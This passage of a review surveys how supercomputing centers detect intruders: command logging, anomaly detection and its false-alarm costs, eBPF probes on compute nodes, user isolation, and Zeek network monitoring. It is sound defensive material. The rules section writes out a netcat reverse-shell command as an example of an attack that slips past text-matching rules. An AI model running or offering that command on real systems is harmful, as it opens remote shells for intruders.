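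Some sites have used smaller tools that only log commands. Brillault compares two of them, Snoopy and execlog. Snoopy is a library that the system loads into each program as it starts, and it logs any command that the program then runs. A program can avoid it by calling the kernel directly, so Brillault does not consider it a security tool. Execlog, CERN's own tool, is a kernel module that records every execution with its arguments. CERN was still testing it in 2013 and has published the code.

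Execlog writes one line per command. In Brillault's sample, an ordinary user runs a program named with three dots, and less than a millisecond later the same process is running as root. It is executing the shell `bash`, but its command line gives the name of the SSH server, presumably as a disguise. The new root user then opens the boot loader's configuration in an editor. Process accounting would probably have kept only one record for that process, under the name "bash", because the process replaced its original program with `bash` before it ended.

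A companion module, netlog, records network connections with the user and process responsible. This is valuable on a login node, where hundreds of people may share one address, so network monitoring cannot identify who opened a connection from the address alone. Brillault warns that logged commands may contain passwords, so sites have to restrict access to these logs.

| Source | What an ordinary user can suppress | What an intruder with root can suppress |
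|---|---|---|
| Shell history | Everything, by disabling or deleting the file | The same, for all users |
| Process accounting | The true name of a tool, by renaming it | Everything, by stopping the service or editing the file |
| auditd | Steps carried out inside a shell or script | Future records, by removing rules or stopping the service, and local copies of old ones |
| osquery | Short commands, if the site relies on snapshots | Future records, by stopping the program |
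| Snoopy | Any command, by bypassing the library | Everything on the machine |
| execlog and netlog | Steps carried out inside a shell or script | Future records, by unloading the modules |

None of these tools can be trusted after an intruder gains root, but the site can protect the record up to that point. Ermopoulos and Yurcik recommend sending the command history to protected servers at regular intervals, though anything since the last transfer remains at risk. Brillault suggests that staff also generate harmless test events and check that they arrive. Otherwise, staff may mistake a host that has stopped sending records for one with little activity.

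### The Los Alamos comparison

Los Alamos National Laboratory tested NERSC's instrumented SSH against auditd in *iSSH v. Auditd* (2012), which it presented at a showcase for students. The laboratory was looking for a way to track an intruder's movements through a supercomputer, because the pattern-matching tools then in use did not do this well enough.

Instrumented SSH was better than auditd at raising alerts on suspicious commands, but it could not tell whether someone had edited, moved or copied a file. Its keystroke records would show a typed copy command but not a copy made by a script. Auditd covered more kinds of activity, including file access, and had better documentation. But its logs recorded both legitimate and malicious behavior, grew large enough to overflow their directories, and led to many false alarms.

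Neither tool clearly performed better. Network benchmarks were about the same with both, and file copies over SSH were faster with the instrumented server, probably because NERSC had included the Pittsburgh patches for fast transfers. The published summary lists strengths and weaknesses but gives no detection rates, so it is weak evidence for choosing between the tools. It does support using them together, since the keystrokes show what a person was trying to do and the audit records show which files and programs were involved. The false alarms reflect the rules and reports at Los Alamos more than auditd itself, which only records what a site selects.

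### Spotting impostors from the commands they run

NCSA researchers tried to find stolen accounts without writing a rule for each attack. They expected an impostor to run different commands than the account's owner would. An impostor might open a chat program, download attack tools and compile them. In 2005 Yurcik and Liu trained a support vector machine, a statistical method that learns to sort cases into classes, on process accounting records. They trained it to distinguish users of a computing cluster from users of an ordinary internet server, who stood in for impostors.

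Ermopoulos and Yurcik report that the method classified 94.9 percent of cases correctly. Of the cases it labeled impostors, 92.4 percent were in the impostor group, and it found 91.9 percent of that group. Accuracy was still 90 percent with ten commands, which suggests that a warning could come early in a session. Using twenty minutes of activity instead of a fixed number of commands gave worse results, because some users run only one command in that time while root may run hundreds.

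They nevertheless judged accuracy of just over 90 percent too low for a production system, which they thought needed more than 99 percent because of the number of users. The test may also have been easier than the real task. Mail programs were among the most common commands on the internet server and help to identify its users, but an intruder on a supercomputer has little reason to read mail there.

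In a month of records, about 50 cluster users each ran more than 30 different commands, and cluster users typically ran a wider variety than the internet users did. Ermopoulos and Yurcik had expected the software on a cluster to limit its users to a small set of commands. The result weakens the idea behind the method, because an impostor can blend in more easily when normal behavior is more varied.

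### Why 99 percent is not enough

Even 99 percent accuracy would be far too low at a center like NERSC, because real intrusions are rare. In 2011 NERSC had 52,000 logins a day and was finding roughly one stolen account a month. A detector that caught every stolen account but wrongly flagged 1 percent of legitimate logins would raise about 520 false alarms a day, or 15,600 in a 30-day month, for one real compromise. If each alarm took ten minutes to check, a day's alarms would take 87 hours, which is full-time work for eleven people.

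| Legitimate logins wrongly flagged | False alarms per day | False alarms per real compromise |
|---|---|---|
| 3.7% | about 1,900 | about 57,000 |
| 1% | 520 | 15,600 |
| 0.1% | 52 | 1,560 |
| 0.01% | about 5 | 156 |
| 0.002% | about 1 | 31 |

The top row is an estimate for the NCSA method. If the method's three scores come from the same set of cases, about a third of those cases were impostors, and the method wrongly flagged about 3.7 percent of the others. With that share of impostors, most of its alarms were correct, but at NERSC almost all of them would have been false.

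A center can reduce the number of false alarms by scoring each account once a day instead of scoring each login. At a 1 percent error rate, NERSC's 4,000 users would trigger at most 40 false alarms a day, or up to 1,200 a month. Even if NERSC was missing nine out of ten compromises, a detector with a 1 percent error rate per login would raise 1,560 false alarms for each actual compromise.

### Rules for specific acts

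Sites therefore tend to prefer rules that flag acts legitimate users have almost no reason to commit. NERSC tells its users that it looks for "recognizably hostile" behavior, and says this kind of monitoring produced few false positives before SSH.

Campbell gives the example of a rule, checked against audit records, that an ordinary user's process should become root only through a few known programs that the system allows to do so. On a well-run machine, staff can list those programs in advance. If a user's second command runs under user number 1234 and the third as root, without a listed program in between, something is probably wrong. The rule doesn't require a model of how a climate scientist or a student normally behaves. It would also detect the kernel attack that the TOSS execution rules probably miss, if the intruder runs another command as root and the site logs it. Campbell's audit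 software could also link a network connection to the user who opened it and flag programs that run from unexpected places.

Rules that match the text of commands are more fragile, because the same attack can be written in different ways. *Democratizing ML for Enterprise Security* (2025) discusses the reverse shell, in which a compromised machine connects out to an attacker and gives them a command prompt. An engineer might change a rule to require the characters `>&` because they appear in a real attack but not in a similar harmless command. This removes the false alarm, but a rule that relied on those characters alone would miss `nc 10.1.1.1 80 -e /bin/sh`, a reverse shell in the paper's own list of attacks.

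A rule can also accurately detect an event that hardly matters. *From Noise to Signal* (2026) describes a test on a Linux machine and lists alerts from the monitoring program Wazuh. The most frequent of these, with 644 occurrences, was for attempts to log in under nonexistent usernames. The rule works as intended, but an intruder with a valid password never triggers it.

Rules and profiles of normal behavior can work together. *A Progress Report on UNICOS Misuse Detection at Los Alamos* (Thompson, Jackson and colleagues, 1995) describes a system that compared activity on the laboratory's Cray supercomputers with each user's past activity and also tested it against experts' rules. Brillault reports that CERN used a modest form of profiling for logins, notifying an account's owner when someone connected from a new location. A false alarm takes a few seconds of the owner's time and none of the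 security staff's, but the approach depends on people reading the messages.

### What newer anomaly detection has changed

Anomaly detection has improved since the NCSA experiments, mostly in company networks. *Facade* (2024) describes a system that Google deployed at large scale to detect insider threats. The system learns which people normally use which resources, taking into account what their peers do. It trains on ordinary logs of document access, database queries and requests to internal services, so it needs no examples of attacks. The paper calls its false positive rate extremely low. A supercomputing center could perhaps treat members of the same research project as peers, but shell commands are a different kind of data from these logs.

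Gelman and Bergeron report in *Sophos AI at Black Hat USA ’25* that anomaly detection often produces high rates of false positives when used to detect malicious commands. They instead used it to find unusual but harmless commands for training a classifier. The classifier thus learns that unusual commands can be legitimate, which a detector on a login node would also need to learn.

*SENTINEL* (2026) presents a method for detecting attackers who use only tools already present on a machine. It caught 81.8 percent of malicious commands while wrongly flagging 0.1 percent of harmless ones. BERT, an established language model, caught 69.7 percent at the same false alarm rate. The test used Windows commands, and the paper notes that no comparable set of labeled Linux commands exists yet. The false alarm rate applies to each command, and users of the cluster in Ermopoulos and Yurcik's study ran 1,853,411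 commands in 28 days, or about 66,000 a day. At 0.1 percent, that cluster would produce about 66 false alarms a day.

Language models can now examine alerts before a person does. *ADR* (2026) describes a deployed system that monitors sessions of AI agents, which are models that run commands by themselves. Analysts found that 34 percent of the sessions it sent them were real problems and 49 percent were false positives. The other 17 percent used real attack techniques without malicious intent, and most of these came from the company's own security testers. The share of real problems is far higher than one in 15,600, but these proportions do not apply to a supercomputer. The most common real problem was exposed credentials, which occur much more often than stolen accounts did at NERSC. Many false positives came from sessions that analyzed large collections of source code, which is an everyday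 activity on a login node.

*Dynamic Reasoning in Next-Gen Detection and Response* (2026) builds this difficulty into its simulated test data. It argues that false positives mostly come from legitimate work that resembles an attack, such as an engineer logging in to production machines with special privileges to fix a fault. It labels these look-alikes separately so researchers can see which kind of work misled a detector. Supercomputing centers would need a similar collection of compilations, debugging sessions and administrators' repairs to find out how the newer methods perform on their users.

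In *Dynamic Factor Graphs for Attack Preemption*, a 2025 supercomputing workshop paper, Cao, Kalbarczyk and Iyer describe a testbed in the live traffic of a supercomputer at NCSA. They say the main obstacle is noisy attack attempts and unreliable alerts, which often hide the real attacks. To stop an attack before it does damage, they use factor graphs, which are statistical models of how uncertain events relate to one another.

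## Watching compute nodes without slowing jobs

Centers have long recorded much less on compute nodes than on login nodes. *Securing the Soft Underbelly of a Supercomputer with BPF Probes* (Wilson, 2020) describes the usual approach, in which a site puts its security controls on a few login nodes and only lightly monitors the nodes behind them. The title borrows a phrase that a US Defense Department representative used at a NIST workshop in 2016, when practitioners had no accepted way to detect malicious activity on compute nodes without missing their performance targets.

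### Why centers watched them lightly

Compute nodes seemed hard to reach because they usually sit on a private network and users normally get to them only through the scheduler. In a reissue of the same paper, Wilson (2021) explains that sites thought gateway controls could be enough if the gateway was the only way in or out.

The nodes also had little of their own to protect. Administrators often load the same read-only operating system image on all of them, so a job cannot alter it. If something goes wrong on a node, staff can reboot it into a clean copy. A diskless node also has no permanent place to keep a log.

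The main objection to monitoring compute nodes was that it would slow jobs. A job often uses every core, so a monitoring program has to take processor time from it, whereas an office laptop has idle cores. According to Wilson, a site may refuse any security measure that reduces performance by more than 1 percent. Parallel jobs are especially sensitive because a delay on one node can hold up all the others.

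This reasoning works well for outsiders who have no account, but poorly for intruders who have stolen credentials. The scheduler accepts jobs from any valid account, so an intruder can run a script on hundreds of nodes, all of which mount the central file systems.

### Checking processes and configurations

One check that takes little compute compares the processes on a node with the jobs that should be running there. Nikhef, the Dutch institute for particle physics, describes its script for this in *Prune User Processes on PBS, Torque Batch Nodes*. The script finds the first process of each current job and traces all its descendants, then kills every other user process except those started by SSH. It is meant to catch processes that outlive their job, either by accident or because a user wants to escape accounting.

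Schedulers can run such checks automatically. LBNL, the laboratory that houses NERSC, publishes Node Health Check, a program that the scheduler starts periodically on each compute node. If a node fails the check, the scheduler can stop sending it jobs. The program mainly looks for faulty hardware and misconfiguration, but a site can use the same mechanism to look for stray processes. A check for stray processes has to account for every way a job can start, or it may kill a legitimate interactive session. It also won't detect a cryptocurrency miner running inside a properly submitted job.

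*Continuous Security and Configuration Monitoring of HPC Clusters* (Garcia-Lomeli, 2015) describes an intern's project at Lawrence Livermore National Laboratory, where administrators had been checking the settings of thousands of nodes by hand. The project put a short shell script on more than 6,000 nodes in over 30 clusters to write each node's operating system and kernel versions to the system log. Splunk, a commercial program for searching logs, gathered the messages from all the nodes, and a reporting tool summarized them.

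About 95 percent of the nodes ran the same release, 3 percent ran a pre-release version of it, and 2 percent ran something else. Another 554 nodes failed to report, and 11 reported when they should not have. Garcia-Lomeli notes that a missing or extra node may be misconfigured, or an intruder may have interfered with its reporting. Most of the 554 were presumably switched off, but the paper doesn't give a breakdown. A version number is weak evidence that a node has no intruder, because an intruder could leave the script running. It is more useful for finding nodes that missed a security update.

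### Recognizing a miner by its use of the machine

Cryptocurrency mining is an obvious way to misuse compute nodes, and job names do not reveal it. *Taxonomist* (Ates, Tuncer and colleagues, 2018) tried to recognize programs from performance data, which many centers already collect. The study used Volta, a 52-node Cray at Sandia National Laboratories, where an existing monitoring system recorded 721 measurements of memory, processor and network use on every node each second.

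After a job ended, the software discarded the first and last 40 seconds of data and reduced each measurement to 11 statistics, such as its mean and 95th percentile. A random forest, a set of decision trees that vote, then compared the result with labeled examples of known programs. If too few trees agreed, the software labeled the program unknown.

The tests included 11 scientific benchmarks, five cryptocurrency miners, a password cracker and 58,366 jobs that 28 ordinary users had run over six months. The method achieved an F-score above 95 percent. The score combines the share of a program's runs that the method finds with how often it is right when it names that program. But the miners ran in benchmark mode and nobody had tried to disguise them. The method also identifies a miner only after the job has finished, although Ates and colleagues think the first few minutes of data would be enough.

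False alarms are less of a problem with jobs than with logins because there are fewer jobs. Volta's users ran about 320 a day, so if the method mistook 1 percent of them for mining, staff would have about three cases a day to check.

*Misuse*, a practitioners' note hosted at RWTH Aachen University in Germany, proposes a simpler rule that raises an alarm when the count of certain specialized processor instructions passes a threshold. Miners often use these instructions, which are uncommon in other HPC work. Some legitimate programs use them too, so the note suggests exempting known users and applications. It does not settle how to collect the counts.

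### Identifying a program from its file

*SIREN* (Jakobsche, Robertsén and colleagues, 2025) examines the program file instead of its behavior. The system loads a small library into each new process, much as Snoopy does on login nodes. The library computes fuzzy hashes, which are short codes built from successive pieces of a file. Similar files have similar codes, whereas an ordinary cryptographic hash changes completely if one bit of the file changes. Malware analysts have used fuzzy hashes for years, and *Using Malware Detection Techniques for HPC Application Classification* (2024) applied them to scientific programs.

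Twelve volunteers tried SIREN on LUMI, a supercomputer in Finland, between December 2024 and March 2025. They ran 13,448 jobs and about 2.3 million processes. One program could not be identified from its name or path, so Jakobsche and colleagues compared six of its hashes with those of known programs and found a perfect match with a copy of icon, a climate and weather code. Other copies of icon showed no measurable similarity to the program as raw files but scored 82 out of 100 for similarity in their function names, so it helps to hash several features separately.

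SIREN sends its data without waiting for confirmation, so a network fault does not hold up a job. NERSC made the same choice for its SSH server. Lost messages left gaps in the records of about 0.02 percent of jobs.

The trial did not include miners or attack tools, and SIREN can identify only programs that resemble ones it has already encountered. It misses programs inside containers, which package software with its own environment, and statically linked programs, which carry their libraries within the file. The system loads SIREN's library through an environment variable, which an intruder could presumably unset. The trial again showed that legitimate work can look odd. One volunteer submitted 11,782 jobs that ran only standard system commands, largely to create directories and delete files.

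### The Brigham Young experiment

Wilson, who administers a cluster at Brigham Young University in Utah, tested whether eBPF could record specific suspicious acts on compute nodes with acceptable overhead. An eBPF program attached to an event is called a probe. It runs every time the event occurs, so its overhead depends heavily on how often that happens. Wilson notes that a probe on memory allocation can slow a program tenfold or more.

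Wilson wanted to know whether a node was contacting outside systems, mining cryptocurrency or connecting suspiciously to other machines, and whether anyone on it was gaining privileges or tunneling out through SSH. Four scripts covered these questions. One recorded lookups of internet names, such as the address of a mining service. Another recorded changes from one user to another, for example when someone became root through `sudo`. A third recorded when an SSH client opened a port to listen for connections, which is a telltale sign of a tunnel. The last recorded new TCP connections to addresses outside the cluster. (TCP is the protocol that carries most web and SSH traffic.)

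Only the tunnel and TCP scripts monitor events in the kernel. The other two attach to functions in shared libraries, so they could miss a statically linked program. Wilson left out UDP because it has no connections, so a probe would have to run for every message.

The test ran High-Performance Linpack, the benchmark used to rank the world's fastest supercomputers, on eight 28-core nodes with identical hardware. Linpack keeps all the cores busy with linear algebra. Wilson ran it on single nodes, pairs, groups of four and all eight, first without the probes and then with them. During the monitored runs, another script on each node simulated an attack every 1 to 15 seconds.

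Wilson reports the differences as percentages of the nodes' theoretical maximum speed. The table gives them as percentages of the speed without probes, which makes them slightly larger.

| Nodes per run | Comparisons | Change in speed with probes |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 8 | Between −0.48% and +0.02% |
| 2 | 4 | Between +0.14% and +0.78% |
| 4 | 2 | +0.11% and +0.15% |
| 8 | 2 | −1.95% and +1.80%; −0.10% on average |

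Probes cannot make a job faster, so the gains must have other causes. Wilson suggests processor temperature and network congestion. Even without probes, the fastest node was about 7 percent faster than the slowest. Still, seven of the eight single nodes ran slower with the probes, and the average slowdown across all eight was 0.2 percent, so the probes may slow jobs slightly. Part of the slowdown could be due to the attack script, which ran only in the monitored tests.

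Wilson calls the eight-node results inconclusive and recommends eBPF based on the smaller runs. The recommendation seems reasonable for this workload, but the experiment is weak evidence about jobs on thousands of nodes. The benchmark also spends most of its time on arithmetic, and programs that constantly open connections would trigger the probes more often.

### What the probes recorded

| Simulated act | Times performed | Log entries | Source of the extra entries |
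|---|---|---|---|
| Name lookup | 1,703 | 19,627 | The benchmark looked up its own nodes |
| Becoming root through `sudo` | 1,720 | 5,160 | Three entries per act |
| SSH tunnel | 1,713 | 3,425 | Two entries per act, with one exception |
| Outside TCP connection | 1,766 | 4,902 | Connections made by the simulated tunnels and name lookups, and the benchmark's connections within a node |

Wilson's conclusion that the probes logged all the attacks is overstated for some name lookups. When the attack script used `dig` or `host`, the log contained only the node's internal address, not the outside site's name. The script picked these two commands about 40 percent of the time, so hundreds of entries lacked the information an analyst would need to see that someone was looking for a mining service.

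The privilege test was also easy. The simulated attacker had permission to use `sudo`, and the probe monitored the library that handles such requests. An attack on a kernel flaw would bypass that library. Campbell's rule for audit records, which detects a process that becomes root without going through an approved program, would be a better defense against that kind of attack.

Most of the noise looks fixable with filters that remove the duplicates and the connections that stay within a node. Covering all users would take more work, because the lookup and privilege scripts each followed a single account.

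### What more frequent events cost

Houssel, Levillain and colleagues (2026), in *A Study of Kernel Telemetry Options for Security-Oriented Provenance*, measured what happens when probes run much more often. On a 24-core server, they accepted 50,000 web connections, wrote 50,000 files and ran a trivial program 50,000 times. They compared four kinds of eBPF probe:

- A kprobe interrupts the processor at almost any chosen kernel function.
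- A tracepoint probe uses a marker that kernel developers have built in.
- A tracing probe jumps directly from the start of a function to the monitoring code, without an interrupt.
- An LSM probe attaches to the kernel's security checks, where it decides whether to allow an operation.

The table shows the increase in processor time.

| Probe and location | Connections | New files | Program runs |
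|---|---|---|---|
| Tracing, at the system call | 0.76% | 8.12% | 1.15% |
| Tracepoint, at the system call | 1.43% | 8.63% | 1.22% |
| Kprobe, at the system call | 1.66% | 9.10% | 1.30% |
| LSM, at the security check, with outcome | 0.89% | 7.27% | 1.13% |
| Tracing, at the security check, with outcome | 1.22% | 10.01% | 2.04% |
| Kprobe, at the security check, with outcome | 1.40% | 12.99% | 2.10% |

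The first three rows cover only attempted operations. Most probes have to run a second time, when the function returns, to record whether the kernel allowed the operation. An LSM probe can avoid this by running after all the other security checks, so it is triggered only by operations they have allowed.

Overhead depended more on which events were recorded than on which probe recorded them. Recording program starts added 1 to 2 percent overhead, while recording new files added at least 7 percent with every method. A simulation that writes a few huge files would probably slow down only slightly, but one that writes millions of small files could slow down badly. These figures are consistent with Wilson's, because Wilson chose events that the benchmark rarely triggered.

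*Waiting at the front door* (2026) shows the same pattern in network monitoring. A tool that probed every kernel function handling packets added more than 25 percent overhead, compared with about 1.5 percent when it probed only a selected few. *eBPF-Based Cybersecurity Mechanisms* (2026), a review of eBPF security tools, puts the overhead of simple packet filtering below 1 percent and that of more comprehensive detection at 3 to 6 percent, more than many centers would accept.

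Filtering events early also reduces overhead. Houssel and colleagues ran the same workload in two containers but wanted records from only one. In the program test, an LSM probe attached only to that container's processes added 0.45 percent overhead. The overhead was 0.85 percent when the probe ran for both containers and discarded the unwanted events, and 1.66 percent when it recorded everything for later sorting. Linux manages each container's processes as a control group, and Wilson suggests using control groups to follow particular jobs. A center could perhaps monitor one suspicious account's jobs closely and leave everyone else's alone. Attaching an LSM probe to a control group requires Linux 6.0 or later.

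Low-overhead records are not always reliable. A program passes a file name to the kernel by giving its location in the program's own memory. An attacker can change the name after a probe has read it but before the kernel uses it, so the log shows a harmless file while the program opens another. Houssel and colleagues found that 69 percent of Linux system calls take at least one argument passed this way. LSM probes avoid this problem because they run after the kernel has made its own copy.

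Monitoring systems also lose records under load. Houssel and colleagues tested four systems that link processes, files and connections into a graph of who did what, and all four lost 90 to 100 percent of events in most workloads. One of them, SPADE, relies on auditd and lost at least 91 percent while adding 13.4 percent to processor time in the program test. Another system, eAudit, lost nothing, but it only records a stream of events and leaves the graph to be built later. It still added 12 percent to processor time in the file test. These were deliberately intense workloads on virtual machines with default settings, so a quiet compute node might lose far less.

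### Keeping users apart

A center can also reduce what it needs to detect. *HPC with Enhanced User Separation* (Prout, Reuther and colleagues, 2024) describes how MIT Lincoln Laboratory isolates its users so that each seems to have a private supercomputer. Linux normally lets every user list everyone's processes, which let researchers study activity on Summit from an ordinary account. Lincoln hides each user's processes and jobs from other users. This setting also protected its systems from a flaw in Slurm before the flaw became public.

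The scheduler gives each compute node to one user at a time, though that user can run several jobs on it. Users can open SSH sessions only on nodes where they have a job. These rules should make monitoring easier, because any unexpected user process either belongs to the wrong account or comes from the node's assigned user.

Lincoln uses a network firewall that controls connections by user. When one process tries to connect to another, the firewall looks up the owner of each process on its machine. It allows the connection if both processes have the same owner or if the two owners share an approved project group. It checks only new connections, which limits the delay. A conventional firewall must be configured with the expected ports and services, which is impractical when users write new programs every day. Lincoln also changed the kernel so that users cannot accidentally open their files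 to everyone.

These measures make it harder for an intruder who steals one account to spy on other users or attack their programs. Staff have less need to detect such attempts when the system blocks them. But the intruder can still read everything the account's owner can read and submit jobs in the owner's name. An intruder who gains root could switch the protections off. Prout and colleagues report better security and reliability but give no figures on incidents before and after the measures were introduced. They acknowledge that some users find the project groups bureaucratic.

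### Accelerators and traffic outside the kernel

Many jobs now run mostly on graphics processors (GPUs). A probe in the kernel can observe the program that sends work to a GPU but not the instructions the GPU executes. Centers can also measure how heavily a GPU is being used. In *Leveraging NVML GPM for NVIDIA GPU Monitoring*, Wassermann, Dollenbacher and colleagues (2026) report four weeks of utilization and energy readings, taken once a minute, from 52 nodes at RWTH Aachen with four Nvidia H100 GPUs each. A GPU that appears busy in such readings could be mining cryptocurrency or training a model.

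*Behavior-Based Detection of GPU Cryptojacking* (2024) describes a detector meant to distinguish miners from other programs by their GPU and memory use. It found eight of ten new miner configurations and wrongly flagged one of five legitimate programs. It is unclear whether the detector would work while another demanding program, such as an AI training run, is using the GPU.

GPUs also keep data in memory after a job ends, and the next user might be able to read it. Lincoln clears the memory between jobs and hides GPUs that the scheduler has not assigned to the user. This prevents a leak that kernel monitoring would probably miss.

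Kernel monitoring can also miss traffic on the fast network between compute nodes, because direct memory transfers can bypass the kernel. Wilson's scripts covered only TCP, and Wilson lists InfiniBand, a common network of this type, as future work. Lincoln's firewall gives some indirect control over these transfers, because most programs first open a TCP connection to arrange them. A program that uses InfiniBand's own connection manager instead avoids both the firewall and any probe on new TCP connections.

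## Joining host records to Zeek network monitoring

A network monitor runs on its own machines, so an intruder with root on a node cannot stop it from recording the node's connections. But its records identify the node only by its address, which all of the node's users share. Host records identify the user and the program but contain little about the traffic. Centers therefore try to match the two sets of records, often using Zeek as the network monitor.

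### Copying and dividing the traffic

Zeek works on a copy of the traffic that crosses the center's border. An optical tap makes the copy by diverting part of the light in each fiber. A mirror port, which is a switch port that repeats the traffic of other ports, costs less but combines both directions of a link into one stream. *PULSAR* (Trivedi, Featherstun and colleagues, 2019) warns that mirror ports easily overload and drop packets. With either method, the original packets do not pass through Zeek, so monitoring does not slow a researcher's transfer. For the same reason, Zeek cannot hold back a suspicious packet and can only signal a router to block later ones.

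According to Zeek's documentation, a Zeek process is limited to a single processor core, so one process cannot handle a fast link. *100G Intrusion Detection* (Stoffer, Sharma and Krous, 2015) describes how Berkeley Lab divided the traffic of its 100-gigabit connection. A switch computes a short number, called a hash, from each packet's two addresses, two ports and protocol, and sends all packets with the same hash to the same machine. The hash has to be symmetric, meaning that it stays the same when source and destination are swapped. Otherwise one machine would receive a user's requests and another the server's replies.

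Five machines each received up to 10 gigabits of traffic per second, and each machine's network card divided its share among ten Zeek processes, called workers. The hardware cost less than $400,000. Ten years later, in *Operationalizing Zeek Deployments*, Welcher and Sharma (2025) still recommend about 1 gigabit per second per worker at the laboratory.

Dividing traffic among Zeek workers can hide an attack. If someone scans thousands of addresses, each worker receives only a few of the attempts, perhaps too few to trigger an alert. The workers therefore share their counts, and a manager process combines their logs. Some workers can also freeze while the others keep running, so the log keeps growing and looks normal. Welcher and Sharma look for this by checking which workers contributed to the last 10,000 lines of the connection log.

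Each worker assembles packets into connections and turns them into events. As Campbell explains, one event can trigger several scripts, so one script can log it while another tests it against the site's policy. The log therefore includes connections that no rule flagged as suspicious, which is valuable when staff learn months later that an attacker was using a particular address.

Large scientific sites still build monitors this way. OLCF's *The Network Intrusion Detection System upgrade shields Oak Ridge Leadership Computing Facility* reports that in April 2025 the Oak Ridge center finished a system that can process 400 gigabits per second from passive taps. It describes the software as open source but doesn't name it. According to SOC WG (2026), a working group on security operations centers, Britain's Science and Technology Facilities Council runs Zeek on ten 100-gigabit links, alongside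 Suricata, which compares traffic with signatures of known attacks. The system misses from under 1 percent to a few percent of the traffic. Berkeley Lab's 2015 system lost about 0.05 percent of packets on average, with peaks of 3 to 4 percent.

A site can deploy the hardware for Zeek without a large expert team. At Purdue University, six undergraduates and two high school students led the deployment of Zeek on four 100-gigabit links, while staff mentored them. Trivedi and colleagues consider the scripts a major challenge, because a site needs someone who can write its policy in Zeek's language and keep it up to date.

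### Leaving large transfers out of the inspection

A small number of connections carry most of the data at a research site. A telescope's nightly upload may occupy a worker for hours without producing anything of interest to security staff. Berkeley Lab removes such transfers from the monitor's copy, a technique called shunting:

1. Zeek identifies a bulk transfer, either because it uses GridFTP, a protocol for moving scientific data, or because it has passed a size limit such as 2 gigabytes.
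2. A script gives the connection's addresses and ports to a small program called Dumbno, which adds a rule to the switch that feeds the workers.
3. The switch stops forwarding the data packets to Zeek but still forwards the packets that control the connection.
4. When the connection ends, Zeek has the rule removed, so old rules do not fill up the switch.

The researcher's transfer continues as before because the rule affects only the copy of the traffic sent to Zeek. Zeek can still log the connection's full duration and size. In one example from Stoffer and colleagues, the laboratory shunted a web download at 150 megabytes, and Zeek logged a total of 154 megabytes over 281 seconds. Shunting reduced the traffic reaching Zeek from around 10 gigabits per second to about 1.

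A newer Zeek package shunts traffic on the monitoring machine itself with XDP, a form of eBPF that can discard packets as they arrive from the network card. *Addressing the Elephant in the Traffic* (Typanski and Grashöfer, 2026) discusses shunting TLS, the encryption that protects websites and many databases. This makes sense because Zeek can read little of a TLS connection after encryption begins.

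Stoffer and colleagues describe shunted connections as presenting no security risk, which seems too strong, because an intruder who copies a research group's data over SSH also produces a large transfer. Shunting loses little in that case, since Zeek could not have read the encrypted files anyway, but staff still need to explain the transfer. The connection log shows how much data left and where it went, but they need host records to find out who sent it.

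### Blocking addresses automatically

NERSC uses NetControl, a part of Zeek that sends blocking instructions to network equipment, to block hosts automatically after certain kinds of alert. Blocked scanners keep trying, and a tap outside the border records every attempt. Zeek's *Reduce conn.log from 35GB to 5GB with a simple hook* (2026) describes NERSC's script of about 15 lines that leaves a connection out of the log if its source is on a list of known scanners and it got no further than its opening packets. The script reduced the daily connection log from 35 gigabytes to between 5 and 7. Zeek still logs any connection that a scanner completes.

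Berkeley Lab keeps records of failed connection attempts. Welcher and Sharma report about 1.6 billion connections a day at the tap outside the lab's border router and 280 million at the tap inside, which suggests that the router blocks more than 80 percent of attempted connections. The lab uses the outer log to track who is attacking it and whether its blocks work, and the inner log for faster searches.

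Automatic blocking also shuts out legitimate users. *Bringing Situational Awareness into Zeek* (Sharma and Banerjee, 2026) gives the example of a blocked home IP address. Staff once had to edit configuration files and restart Zeek everywhere to lift such a block. The restart erased Zeek's data on attacks in progress, and only senior engineers could carry out the procedure safely. Zeek now rereads lists of exceptions and hostile addresses while it runs, so anyone on the team can correct a mistaken block with one command.

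These lists can also cause problems. A scheduled task once emptied the laboratory's file of blocked addresses, though Zeek detected the missing data and kept its old entries. A timing error that took more than eight years to appear caused the system to block addresses at CERN. Sharma and Banerjee worry most about lists that silently stop updating, so the laboratory raises an alert if any list goes more than 24 hours without a change.

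Purdue's team was more cautious. It collected alerts on scans and SSH password guessing for six months before settling on criteria for blocking, and it was still testing the blocks in 2019. Such criteria are suited to detecting attackers who try many addresses or passwords, but not an intruder who uses a stolen credential.

### Matching a connection to a user

The table shows an invented example in which Zeek logs a large upload from a login node, along with the audit record that staff would hope to find on the node.

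| Property | Zeek connection record | Audit record |
|---|---|---|
| Time | 14:03:22.41 | 14:03:22.40 |
| Source | 192.0.2.17, port 51514 | Node login07; no address or port |
| Destination | 203.0.113.50, port 443 | 203.0.113.50, port 443 |
| Duration and data sent | 41 minutes, 3.2 gigabytes | Missing |
| User | Missing | mchen, login session 4471 |
| Program | Missing | `/dev/shm/.x/sync`, process 31877 |

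An analyst first looks up the source address and finds that it belongs to login07. The analyst then searches that node's audit records for a process that called `connect`, the system call that opens a connection, with the same destination address and port at about the same time. If only one record matches, its process, 31877, opened the connection. Earlier records for that process show when the program started and with which arguments. The session number identifies other commands from the same login, and the SSH log shows where the user connected from.

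A legitimate upload to a web service could easily produce the same Zeek record. The audit record shows that the program was in a hidden directory in memory, but not that it sent 3.2 gigabytes. Together, the two records give staff good reason to call the account's owner.

The audit record lacks the source port because it contains only what the program passed to the kernel (Haas, Sommer and Fischer, *zeek-osquery*, 2020). A program that calls `connect` supplies the destination and normally leaves the kernel to choose the local port. If two users of login07 contact the same software repository in the same second, an analyst cannot tell from the audit records which user opened which connection.

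The kernel's list of open sockets, the endpoints that programs use for network connections, includes the local port. But the list misses short connections that open and close between readings. Haas and colleagues therefore combine the two sources.

### Auditd records in Zeek at NERSC

NERSC had already built a way to send data from its instrumented SSH server to Zeek, and Campbell used much the same method for auditd. The software that prepares the audit records for Zeek has to run on each node, because user IDs and system call numbers can differ between machines.

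Zeek keeps a lasting record of the user's identities in each login session and attaches individual actions to that record. According to Campbell's 2015 slides, the network records cover outgoing connections and listeners (programs waiting for others to connect). Each network record includes the node, the session and the user. But the source address and port of an outgoing connection are normally blank, so staff would face the same ambiguity as in the example above.

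In this design, Zeek can also use host records that have no matching network traffic. Campbell's rule for detecting unexpected switches to root checks identities at intervals, so it does not flag legitimate programs such as `ping` that run as root only for a moment. In the sample alert, an ordinary user has become root through a program called `/var/tmp/x`.

Another component builds a login history for each user from instrumented SSH, system logs and Globus. It raises an alert when someone logs in from a new country. Staff can then compare the alert with what the person did in the session.

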